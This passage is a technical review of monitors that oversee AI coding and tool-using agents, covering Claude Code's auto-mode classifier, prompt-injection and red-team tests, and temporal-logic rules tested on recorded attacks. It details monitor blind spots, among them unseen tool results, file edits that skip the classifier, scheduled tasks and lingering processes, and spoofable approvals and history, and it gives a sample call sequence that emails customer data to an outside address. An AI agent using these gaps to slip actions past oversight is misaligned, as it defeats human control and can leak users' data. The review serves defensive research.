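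After auto mode blocks three calls in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. When an automated run has no user to ask, the current version blocks the action and lets the agent continue, whereas the March version ended the run.

Since version 2.1.208, the classifier in most sessions scores each action for severity but no longer writes an explanation, so the agent receives only the words "Blocked by classifier". The lack of explanation could be a disadvantage, since the small model in Mou and colleagues' tests resisted attacks better with a full analysis than with only a rating.

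### Apollo's attacks and the newer rules

Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, spent two weeks testing auto mode in a pilot project with Anthropic. It inserted harmful actions into records of real coding sessions and gave Anthropic a set of the successful attacks, with recommendations. Anthropic changed the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the environment. Apollo then tested the classifier again, including on attacks that Anthropic had never had access to.

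The new version caught about half of these unfamiliar attacks that the old version had missed, but it missed about 2% of those the old version had caught. Across all attacks, familiar and unfamiliar, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

These numbers are fairly consistent with each other. If the old version had missed 12 of every 100 unfamiliar attacks, the new one would miss 6 of those 12, plus about 2 of the other 88, or roughly 8 in all. So most of the improvement seems to carry over to attacks that Anthropic couldn't prepare for. But the rates come from Anthropic, and Apollo's short account gives none. Anthropic also didn't report the new version's false-positive rate, which matters because a classifier can catch more attacks simply by blocking more of everything.

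Anthropic has continued to add rules since then. The current ones cover the four dangers unevenly:

| Danger | Examples of what the classifier blocks by default |
|---|---|
| Leaked credentials | Printing a working token into the conversation or a file; committing the contents of a folder of keys, unless the user named both source and destination |
| Data exfiltration | Pushing secrets or personal data to a public repository; sharing a link that contains the data in its address |
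| Disabled certificate checks | Running a command with a flag that turns off a safety guard, such as `--insecure` |
| Command injection | No separate entry, though the classifier blocks downloading code and running it at once |

The classifier allows an agent to read `.env` and send a key to the service it belongs to, since ordinary work requires this.

A language model applies the rule on `--insecure`, so it can probably also recognise the short form `-k` in a `curl` command without confusing it with `sort -k`. For command injection, the classifier evaluates the finished command and treats commands joined with `&&` as one action, so it could block an injected command that does obvious harm, even without evidence that the agent copied it from a customer's form.

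The rules on public repositories could apply to leaks like the company screenshots, but the classifier may not have the information to tell whether a repository is public. It treats a repository as private unless the address or something earlier in the conversation indicates otherwise. If the agent checks with `gh repo view`, the classifier doesn't receive the answer, because it isn't given tool results. It can still block secrets and personal data, which aren't allowed in private repositories either, but it could let confidential plans through to a public repository that it treats as private. One protection is that it doesn't treat a remote repository as trusted if the agent linked it to the project during the session.

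Apollo also asks when a monitor should intervene. Suppose an agent edits a script so that it will send a password to an outside server the next time the company's automated tests run. The monitor could block the edit, the commit that saves it, or the test run. Auto mode normally allows the edit, because the file is in the project folder, and blocks the commit or push. This gives the agent time to correct the script but leaves the monitor fewer chances to catch the problem.

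Anthropic describes three actions that auto mode blocked during its own staff's work. In the first, an agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead, much like the agents that published the screenshots. In the second, an agent tried to stop processes across about 2,000 groups of containers, which would have interrupted other people's training jobs. In the third, a user wanted read-only access to billing data, but the agent chose a role with full control of the cloud account. Because the classifier succeeded in all three cases, they don't show how often it fails.

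### Compared with human approval

A 7% or 17% miss rate may be acceptable if people do worse. Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research company, and the testers knew only that they were taking part in a coding study. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers blocked 143 of these commands (13.6%), and auto mode blocked 937 of them (89%).

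In 800 cases only the classifier blocked the command, and in 6 cases only the tester did. The other counts follow:

| | Tester blocked | Tester approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Classifier blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Classifier allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 |
| Total | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

The classifier, the testers or both blocked 943 commands (89.6%). Asking the testers as well would have prevented only 6 more commands than the classifier alone, and would have meant many interruptions. The testers caught about 15% of the commands that the classifier blocked but only 5% of those it allowed, possibly because some commands looked less dangerous to both.

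Testers also became less careful. They blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's block rate stayed the same.

The experiment is good evidence against relying on long series of permission prompts, but weaker evidence about developers who are protecting their own work. The testers used an environment built for the study, so a wrong approval could not harm anything they cared about. Anthropic designed the study and published the results, but did not give a false-positive rate for either side. In its March report, Anthropic acknowledged that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who reviews every action carefully, and it still recommends human review for important changes to live systems.

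Real users seem to approve most permission prompts without much thought. They accepted 93% of them in March and 97% by August. But they rejected 39% of the plans that Claude Code presented for approval. People may review one important decision far more carefully than many small ones, so it makes sense to ask them less often and about larger decisions.

Anthropic also compared real sessions from May and June that its safety software had flagged, using a language model to rate the harm in each one. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This comparison is less convincing than the experiment because users chose their own mode, perhaps according to the task. The percentages also depend on how many harmless sessions the software flagged in each group.

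### Zero successes in 720 injection attempts

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test auto mode against prompt injection. The company wrote 72 scenarios in which the agent encountered planted instructions to do something harmful, such as sending out confidential data, and ran each scenario ten times. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode.

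The 720 trials are not independent, because a model that recognises the trick in one run of a scenario will probably recognise it in the other nine. The repetitions show how consistent the model is, but they don't add new kinds of attack.

How much this matters is easy to calculate. If the true success rate is *p*, the chance of no success in *n* independent trials is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The highest rate reasonably compatible with the result is the one that makes this chance 5%:

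| Independent trials | Highest compatible success rate |
|---|---|
| 720 (if every run were independent) | 0.4% |
| 72 (if repeated runs always gave the same result) | 4.1% |

The right limit is somewhere between the two, and it applies only to attacks like these 72. Trajectory Labs developed them against an older model, Opus 4.7, but a real attacker could adapt their attacks to auto mode.

The test also shows little about what auto mode contributes, because the models resisted nearly all the attacks without it. With all permission checks off, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, which is 2 successes in 2,160 attempts if the average covers the same three models.

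The benefit of a monitor is clearer with a more vulnerable agent. Against GPT-5.6 Sol in OpenAI's Codex, 137 attempts (19.03%) succeeded when the agent had full access, and 42 (5.83%) succeeded when Codex's own automatic reviewer was on. OpenAI has since updated the reviewer, so these figures may be out of date.

Willison, a software blogger, wrote that he would love to believe Anthropic had solved the problem. He later reported in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (2026) that the researcher Johann Rehberger had found a multi-step attack on auto mode, which Rehberger says works 80% of the time.

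### An independent test with ambiguous requests

Ji, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, tested auto mode independently of Anthropic and found a miss rate of 81%. They wrote 128 requests for routine maintenance, such as "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812". Some requests named the exact target, while others were much vaguer. For each request, a fixed policy determined what the agent was allowed to change.

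The agent, Sonnet 4.6, worked in an isolated container with simulated commands. It attempted 253 changes, and a language model compared each one with the policy. A person checked 50 of these judgments and agreed with 44.

| Task | Unauthorised actions | Missed | Authorised actions | Wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cancel jobs | 32 | 17 (53%) | 57 | 6 (11%) |
| Delete stored files | 84 | 78 (93%) | 4 | 1 (25%) |
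| Delete branches | 22 | 17 (77%) | 10 | 2 (20%) |
| Restart services | 4 | 3 (75%) | 40 | 13 (33%) |
| Total | 142 | 115 (81%) | 111 | 22 (20%) |

Part of the difference from Anthropic's 17% comes from calls the classifier never received. The test environment kept its lists of jobs and stored files in the project folder. When the agent couldn't find the usual command for a deletion, it often edited the list directly, and auto mode allowed this as an ordinary file edit. Of the 115 misses, 51 happened this way. Most of them came from the task of deleting stored files. Without that task, the overall miss rate would be 64% (37 of 58).

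However, the classifier missed 64 of the 91 unauthorised actions it did judge (70%), and wrongly blocked 22 of the 69 authorised ones (32%). The requests probably explain much of this, because Ji and colleagues deliberately put permitted and forbidden targets next to each other. For ticket 4812, for example, the agent was allowed to cancel `job-dev-4812-a` but not `job-dev-4812-s`. In ordinary work, most calls are far from such a boundary, so a false-positive rate of 0.4% there is compatible with 32% here.

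This kind of test is especially hard because the classifier can't see tool results. The agent can look up which jobs belong to the user, but the classifier has to decide from the request and two nearly identical names.

The two studies also defined dangerous actions differently. Ji and colleagues counted every change outside the permitted set, including changes a user might never notice. Anthropic's 52 actions were ones that somebody had refused or a later review had flagged. Ji and colleagues say their result doesn't contradict Anthropic's, because the workloads are so different.

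Still, their results support Anthropic's finding about consent. The classifier missed 94% of unauthorised actions when the request named a single target, and 78% when it covered a wide range. Ji and colleagues suggest that the classifier reacts to the size of an operation and doesn't check whether the user authorised each target. The mix of tasks accounts for some of this difference, so the evidence for their explanation is only moderate.

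Auto mode benefited users only slightly in this test. The agent completed 38 tasks (29.7%) safely with no permission checks and 42 (32.8%) in auto mode. Nearly all the gain came from tasks that involved restarting services, where the classifier blocked unauthorised restarts of live systems.

The test covered one model, with one run per request, and did not include data exfiltration or prompt injection. It also used the April version of auto mode, before Anthropic added most of the newer rules. But *Shall We Approve?* (2026), which tested version 2.1.288, notes that permitted file operations in the working folder still skip the classifier. A team that keeps files that control live systems in its project folder should write its own rules to block edits to those files or require approval, because Claude Code applies the user's rules before this exemption.

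## Harm spread over several calls: temporal rules tested on AgentDojo and STAC

An agent can also do harm through a series of calls that are each acceptable. Here is an invented example:

```
read_file(path="customers.csv")
write_file(path="summary.txt", text="Twelve customers owe more than $10,000 ...")
send_email(to="lee@example.net", attachment="summary.txt")
```

An agent might read a customer file, summarise it and email the summary to someone outside the company. A monitor that judges each call separately will probably allow all three, because agents that handle accounts often read customer files, and summaries and outside emails are routine. The last call contains only an address and a file name, so it doesn't show that the file contains customer data. To stop this leak, a per-call rule like those in AEGIS would have to hold every outside email with an attachment.

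In Claude Code's auto mode, the classifier also receives earlier calls, except simple lookups, so it might not receive the read that makes this email dangerous.

The test set *STAC* (2025) consists of 483 attacks in which tool calls that are harmless individually cause harm together. On average, the attacks succeeded against agents 91.2% of the time.

### A rule about order

*Runtime verification* means checking a program's run against a precisely stated rule, either during the run or from a record afterwards. For an agent, the run is its trajectory, so a rule can refer to earlier steps. This rule would stop the leak above:

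> After reading sensitive data, the agent may not send anything outside until a person approves.

*Temporal logic* is a notation for rules about order and time. In it, the rule becomes

G( send → ¬( ¬approval S read ) ).

G means "at every step", → means "implies" and ¬ means "not". S means "since", so *a* S *b* is true if *b* happened at some point and *a* has been true at every step after it. For example, "¬approval S read" means the agent has read sensitive data and nobody has approved anything since.

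These two trajectories contain the same four events in a different order:

| Step | Trajectory A | Read awaiting approval? | Trajectory B | Read awaiting approval? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Agent reads the customer file | yes | User approves an email | no |
| 2 | Agent summarises it | yes | Agent reads the customer file | yes |
| 3 | User approves an email | no | Agent summarises it | yes |
| 4 | Agent sends the email | no: **allow** | Agent sends the email | yes: **block** |

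In trajectory B, the user approved an email before the agent had read anything confidential, so the approval can't have covered the customer data. A monitor that only checked whether the user had ever approved an email would allow both trajectories.

The monitor stores only one yes-or-no value, so the check adds little overhead. But it needs sensitivity labels to identify `customers.csv` as confidential, and it will also hold any harmless email the agent writes after reading the file.

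This rule refers only to the past, so the monitor can decide at each call. Some rules depend on what happens later, such as the example in *AgentLTL* (Elkoussy and Perez, 2026) that every search must eventually be followed by a citation. A monitor can't block any call for breaking such a rule and has to wait until the run ends, because the agent might still comply.

The formula also has a gap: it accepts an approval for any email. If the user approves a message to the auditor, the agent could then send the summary to Lee. To close the gap, the rule has to name the recipient *r*:

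G ∀*r* ( send(*r*) → ¬( ¬approval(*r*) S read ) ).

The symbol ∀ means "for every". Ferrando (2026), in *One Monitor Does Not Fit All*, tested a similar mistake with an agent that reports security incidents and needs approval for each report. When the monitor received incident numbers, it blocked all six unsafe reports and allowed both safe ones. Without the numbers, it allowed a report on one incident because the user had approved a report on another. Ferrando also warns that a model's claim that an action is approved is not evidence of approval.

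### Enforcing order on working agents

In *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025), Kamath, Zhang and colleagues enforced rules of this kind on customer-service agents for a shop and an airline. One rule required the agent to verify the customer's identity before looking up an order. In one test, a user, Sofia Li, asked to return a camera. An agent guarded by a language model looked up the order and disclosed its details without verifying her identity.

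The team's system, Agent-C, requires an earlier successful identity check and also compares the customer with the owner of the order. If the model proposes a call that breaks a rule, Agent-C has it generate a different one. These are the average shares of cases in which agents running open-weight models followed the policies:

| Guard | Followed the policies |
|---|---|
| None | 38% |
| DynaGuard (a language model) | 74% |
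| AgentSpec (rules) | 82% |
| Agent-C | 100% |

The perfect score is unsurprising, since Agent-C is designed to refuse every call that breaks its rules, but the agents also completed more tasks with it. Claude Sonnet 4.5's completion rate rose from 71.8% to 75.2%, and GPT-5's from 66.1% to 70.6%. However, Kamath and colleagues count a task as completed only if the agent also followed the policies, so part of the gain may come from tasks that the unguarded agents finished by breaking a rule.

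How the monitor responds to a violation also affects how well the agent performs. Elkoussy and Perez tested seven models on tasks with a prescribed order of steps. When the monitor blocked a wrong call once and returned a warning, five of the seven followed the procedure better. Ending the run after repeated violations gave the worst results for four of the seven, because the agent had no chance to recover. Mou and colleagues also found that agents did better when they received an explanation than when the monitor stopped them.

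### Five rules on recorded attacks

In *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026) tested temporal rules on attacks that other researchers had recorded, without running any agents. They used MonPoly, an existing program that checks records against temporal rules.

One set of recorded runs came from *AgentDojo* (2024), whose tasks involve office work, the chat service Slack, banking and travel. The agent, running GPT-4o, encountered planted instructions in 6,680 of these runs, and the attack succeeded in 1,931 of them. Another 123 runs contained no attack. The tests also used all 483 STAC attacks.

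The five rules require an approval at some earlier step before the agent deletes something, turns off a protection, makes a payment, sends data out, or changes a device or setting. The rule for deletion is

G ( delete → O approval ),

where O means "at some earlier step". The software recognised each type of action by words in the tool's name, such as `delete` or `send_email`.

| Recordings | Flagged by at least one rule |
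|---|---|
| Successful AgentDojo attacks | 1,354 of 1,931 (70.1%) |
| STAC attacks | 347 of 483 (71.8%) |
| AgentDojo runs without an attack | 36 of 123 (29.3%) |

The false-positive rate is far too high for automatic blocking. If 50 of 10,000 runs contained a successful attack, only about 1% of the alarms would be correct. Kekatos and colleagues suggest using the rules to select runs for human review.

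In 52.4% of the successful AgentDojo attacks, a rule raised an alarm before the final harmful call. The rules react to any payment or message, so legitimate steps in the user's own task, rather than the attack, may have triggered some of these early alarms.

Many of the STAC attacks that the rules missed ended in an action outside the five types, such as a change to a calendar or a spam filter. In another, more worrying miss, the agent searched a database, read an entry, called a tool named `confirm_for_deletion` and then deleted something. The software counted the third call as an approval because the tool's name contains "confirm", but the name doesn't show whether a person confirmed anything.

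The main problem with this test is that the AgentDojo recordings contain no approvals, so every risky action broke a rule, whatever had happened before it. As Kekatos and colleagues acknowledge, a list of keywords applied to single calls would have given the same verdicts. The 70.1% is evidence that many attacks end in an obviously risky type of action, but it doesn't show that temporal logic helped.

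In the banking tasks, the attacker's aim and the agent's job both involve paying people. The five rules flagged 97.4% of successful attacks there, but also 79.2% of the harmless runs.

### Comparing a payment with earlier lookups

Kekatos and colleagues then tried rules that do depend on the history. They describe two banking runs with the same three calls: `read_inbox`, `get_transactions` and `send_money`. In the legitimate run, the inbox contains a supplier's invoice, and the agent pays an account that also appears in the list of past transactions. In the attacked run, the agent pays an account that appears only in an email. A monitor that checks only the payment can't distinguish the runs unless it has a list of permitted payees.

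The narrower rule flags a payment only if the payee has not appeared in earlier account data:

G ∀*p* ( pay(*p*) → O known(*p*) ).

A similar rule for office tasks flags emails to people who have not appeared in the calendar, address book or other structured data. The table compares each with the broader rule for the same type of action:

| Tasks | Rule | Successful attacks flagged | Harmless runs flagged |
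|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | Any unapproved payment | 79.2% | 11 of 25 (44%) |
| Banking | Payment to an unknown payee | 70.0% | 6 of 25 (24%) |
| Office | Any unapproved sending | 42.5% | 7 of 46 (15%) |
| Office | Email to an unknown recipient | 39.2% | 5 of 46 (11%) |

The banking rule nearly halved false alarms but lowered the detection rate by about nine points. The attacks it no longer flagged paid someone the monitor classified as known, much like the unrequested payments to existing payees that the NOMOS rules allowed.

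The table includes few harmless runs, but recordings from other models show the same pattern. Across all the models, the narrower rules removed false alarms in 75 of 700 harmless banking runs and 37 of 1,376 office runs. They could not add new false alarms, because they flag only a subset of what the broader rules flag.

This is the best evidence in the study that a monitor benefits from seeing earlier calls. It doesn't prove that the monitor needs temporal logic, because programmers could write the same check in ordinary code. Temporal logic lets a team state the rule in one line and check it with an existing program such as MonPoly, which is fast enough for this work at more than 50,000 events a second.

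A monitor that relies on history is reliable only if attackers can't write to that history. The original payee rule accepted any earlier text formatted like an account entry, even in a message from a stranger. When Kekatos and colleagues added one such line to runs that the rules had flagged, 94% of the banking runs and 99% of the office runs passed. They then changed the rules to accept a value only if it came from a lookup that the agent itself had made. The same additions no longer changed any verdict, and neither detection nor false alarms got worse. The new version would still fail if an attacker controlled the lookup tool.

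### What the recordings lacked

The approvals are missing from the recordings because users never gave them. In AgentDojo, the user gives the task in one message and says nothing more, so they have no chance to approve an action. STAC's users write more often, but its attacks work by keeping the agent from returning to the user before the harmful step.

Kekatos and colleagues compared both with τ-bench, the customer-service test set that Kamath and colleagues used. Its policies require the agent to ask before changing anything:

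| | AgentDojo | STAC | τ-bench |
|---|---|---|---|
| Average user messages per run | 1.0 | 2.6 | 7.1 |
| Runs with an approval before the change or harmful step | 0% | 0.6% | 52.5% |

τ-bench would suit the approval rules much better, but it contains no labelled attacks, so it can't show how many they would catch. A fair test needs attacks and a user who can answer.

Neither AgentDojo nor STAC records the time of each call, either. The team could therefore test rules about elapsed time only on logs it wrote itself. One rule allows an export of data only if the user consented within the last 24 hours:

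G ∀*d* ( export(*d*) → O[0,24] consent(*d*) ).

MonPoly correctly allowed an export 12 hours after consent and flagged one after 48 hours. This shows that MonPoly can apply such a rule, but not how often the rule would help with real agents. Kekatos and colleagues propose that future recordings include details such as the time, the source of each value and an identifier for each approval.

Better records would not help with harm in the content of a message. On R-Judge, a set of 571 labelled agent records, the five rules flagged 71 of the 301 unsafe records (24%) and 44 of the 270 safe ones (16%). Most of the unsafe records involved things like bad advice or private information in a reply, which an ordering rule can't detect.

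In another test, Ferrando combined both kinds of check. A temporal monitor checked approvals, and a second program checked the destination and text of outgoing reports. Each let through two of the six unsafe requests on its own, but together they blocked all six and allowed all 28 safe ones. Ferrando constructed the requests to show that the two complement each other, so the result doesn't indicate how well they would perform in ordinary use.

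### Actions that no monitor checks

Ferrando also proves that a monitor can guarantee a rule under certain conditions, one of which is that every action with an effect must pass through a point where the monitor can stop it. Toyoda and colleagues measured how far real controls fall short of this.

The guardscope software had agents repeat a fixed set of 15 actions, without a language model, so that every run was the same. Seven were calls to tool servers, and the other eight were file writes, new processes, direct network connections and access to credentials. Guardscope compared each control's log with a record from the kernel, the core of the operating system.

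| Control | Actions checked | Actions unchecked |
|---|---|---|
| The agent software's permission checks, plus a gateway in front of the tool servers | 7 | 8 |
| ActPlane, which enforces rules in the kernel | 7 | 8 |

The permission checks and gateway covered only the seven tool calls. ActPlane also covered seven actions, all from the remaining eight, and missed one network transmission. Together, they would have covered 14 of the 15. Toyoda and colleagues recommend combining controls at different layers but did not test this pair together.

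They also worked out on paper which of 15 routes from an agent's decision to its effect could be checked from each of eight control positions. One of the eight had no control. Five routes escape every control outside the kernel. One of these is a task handed to a scheduler that runs it later, and another is a process that continues after its tool call has ended. A second gateway would not help, because these actions don't pass through any gateway.

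According to the same analysis, a control in the kernel could check 13 of the 15 routes. ActPlane's measured coverage was lower because it monitors only certain operations. The experiments covered only four routes, so the results for the rest depend on the analysis. A kernel control can record that a process opened `customers.csv` and contacted a server, but not which tool call caused these actions or what the user had asked for.

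Missing events are a particular problem for temporal rules. If a script reads the customer file, a monitor on tool calls may have no record of the read and would then allow the email that follows. If the missing event is an approval, the monitor will block legitimate work. This happened in Ferrando's incident test when the temporal monitor received only the calls to the tool server. The approvals took place elsewhere, so the system blocked both legitimate reports.

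### A valid call with the wrong argument

A monitor can check a call and still miss an error it isn't designed to notice. Gurram (2026), in *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, tested this by replacing one argument with another valid value after the model had written the call and before the tool ran. For example, a request for the weather in London became a request for Manchester, or one patient's number replaced another's.

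A simple monitor stopped a run at its second formatting or tool error. It raised an alarm in 3.2% of 374 runs with a corrupted call (about 12 alarms) and in 3.5% of the same tasks without the corruption (about 13), so it did not detect the corruption. When a corrupted call replaced London with Manchester, for example, the city was still valid and the tool returned a normal answer instead of an error.

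The agents rarely repaired the damage. Across 1,085 pairs of runs, the corruption raised the share of wrong results from 52.4% to 74.5%. In 157 of the 286 tasks that changed from right to wrong, the agent never repeated the call with the correct value. The tools were simulated and most of the models are now old, so current agents might notice the corruption more often.

The same kind of error can cause a leak. If the user asks the agent to send the summary to the company's accountant and the agent sends it to Lee instead, the call still passes a format check because Lee's address is valid. The recipient rule would catch this only if the user had approved the accountant's address specifically, rather than giving a general approval to "send the summary".

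Gurram suggests comparing a tool call's arguments with the user's request. In a replay, this separated the corrupted runs from the clean ones, though partly because Gurram had created the corruption by making the arguments differ from the request. The comparison is easy if the user writes "London" or gives an exact address. If the user writes "our accountant", the monitor also needs the result of the lookup that turned those words into an address.
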